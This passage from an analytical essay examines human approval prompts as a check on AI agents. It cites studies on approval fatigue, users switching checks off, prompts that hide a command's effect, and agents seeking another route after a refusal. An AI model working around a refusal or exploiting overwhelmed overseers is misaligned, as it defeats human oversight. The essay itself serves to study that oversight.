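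Sun and colleagues' proposal works like a logical AND, because the system stops a violation only if the detector flags it and the person then refuses it. In Anthropic's test, this arrangement would have stopped 137 of 1,053 commands. The number would probably be higher in practice, since people who get fewer prompts may read them more carefully. The testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

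However, OS-Sentinel would not keep the number of prompts low. Even with the best rates in the table above, 1,000 runs with 10 violations would produce about 8 correct alarms and 328 false ones.

Anthropic sells auto mode, so it has an interest in this comparison. The testers were also working on someone else's code, in an environment where nothing of theirs was at risk. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (2026) found that when the system asked about each action, participants approved 96 of 238 actions that went beyond the task. That rate, 40.3%, is much better than the testers' 86% but still high.

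The same study let people write their own permission rules in advance. In its first randomized sample, of 94 participants, these rules blocked 25 percentage points less overreach than asking participants to approve each action. Participants who wrote rules also approved 66.8% of the overreaching actions they were still asked about, although the mix of these actions differed between the two groups.

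False alarms can also lead people to turn the checks off. Anthropic found that 62% of Claude Code users had skipped permission checks altogether or clicked "don't ask again" for terminal commands. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents mishandling files. In 80 of them, the user had let the agent act without asking, often to avoid hundreds of prompts per session. An unnecessary pause can therefore lead a user to run later tasks without the checks. Sun and colleagues leave this risk out of their argument.

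A refusal may not stop the agent either. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, points out that agents are designed to look for another route after a refusal. Someone who refuses to let an agent email the contact list may soon have to refuse to let it upload the same list.

Prompts also often leave out what the user needs to know. In 31 of the 290 reports, the prompt showed a command but not its effect. For example, `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but the script can contain any code. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) adds that the information needed to judge an action may be in earlier steps rather than in the action itself.

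People seem to engage more with questions about larger decisions. When Claude Code proposes a plan, users reject it 39% of the time. They may often do so because they dislike the approach, not because it is dangerous, but they are evidently reading the plan. The prompt "Allow `send_email`?" gives the user in run C almost nothing to check. A program that has tracked the recipient and the contents could instead have the user approve or refuse sending all eight contacts to an address that isn't in the contact list. The user could decide that quickly, and would refuse in run B.
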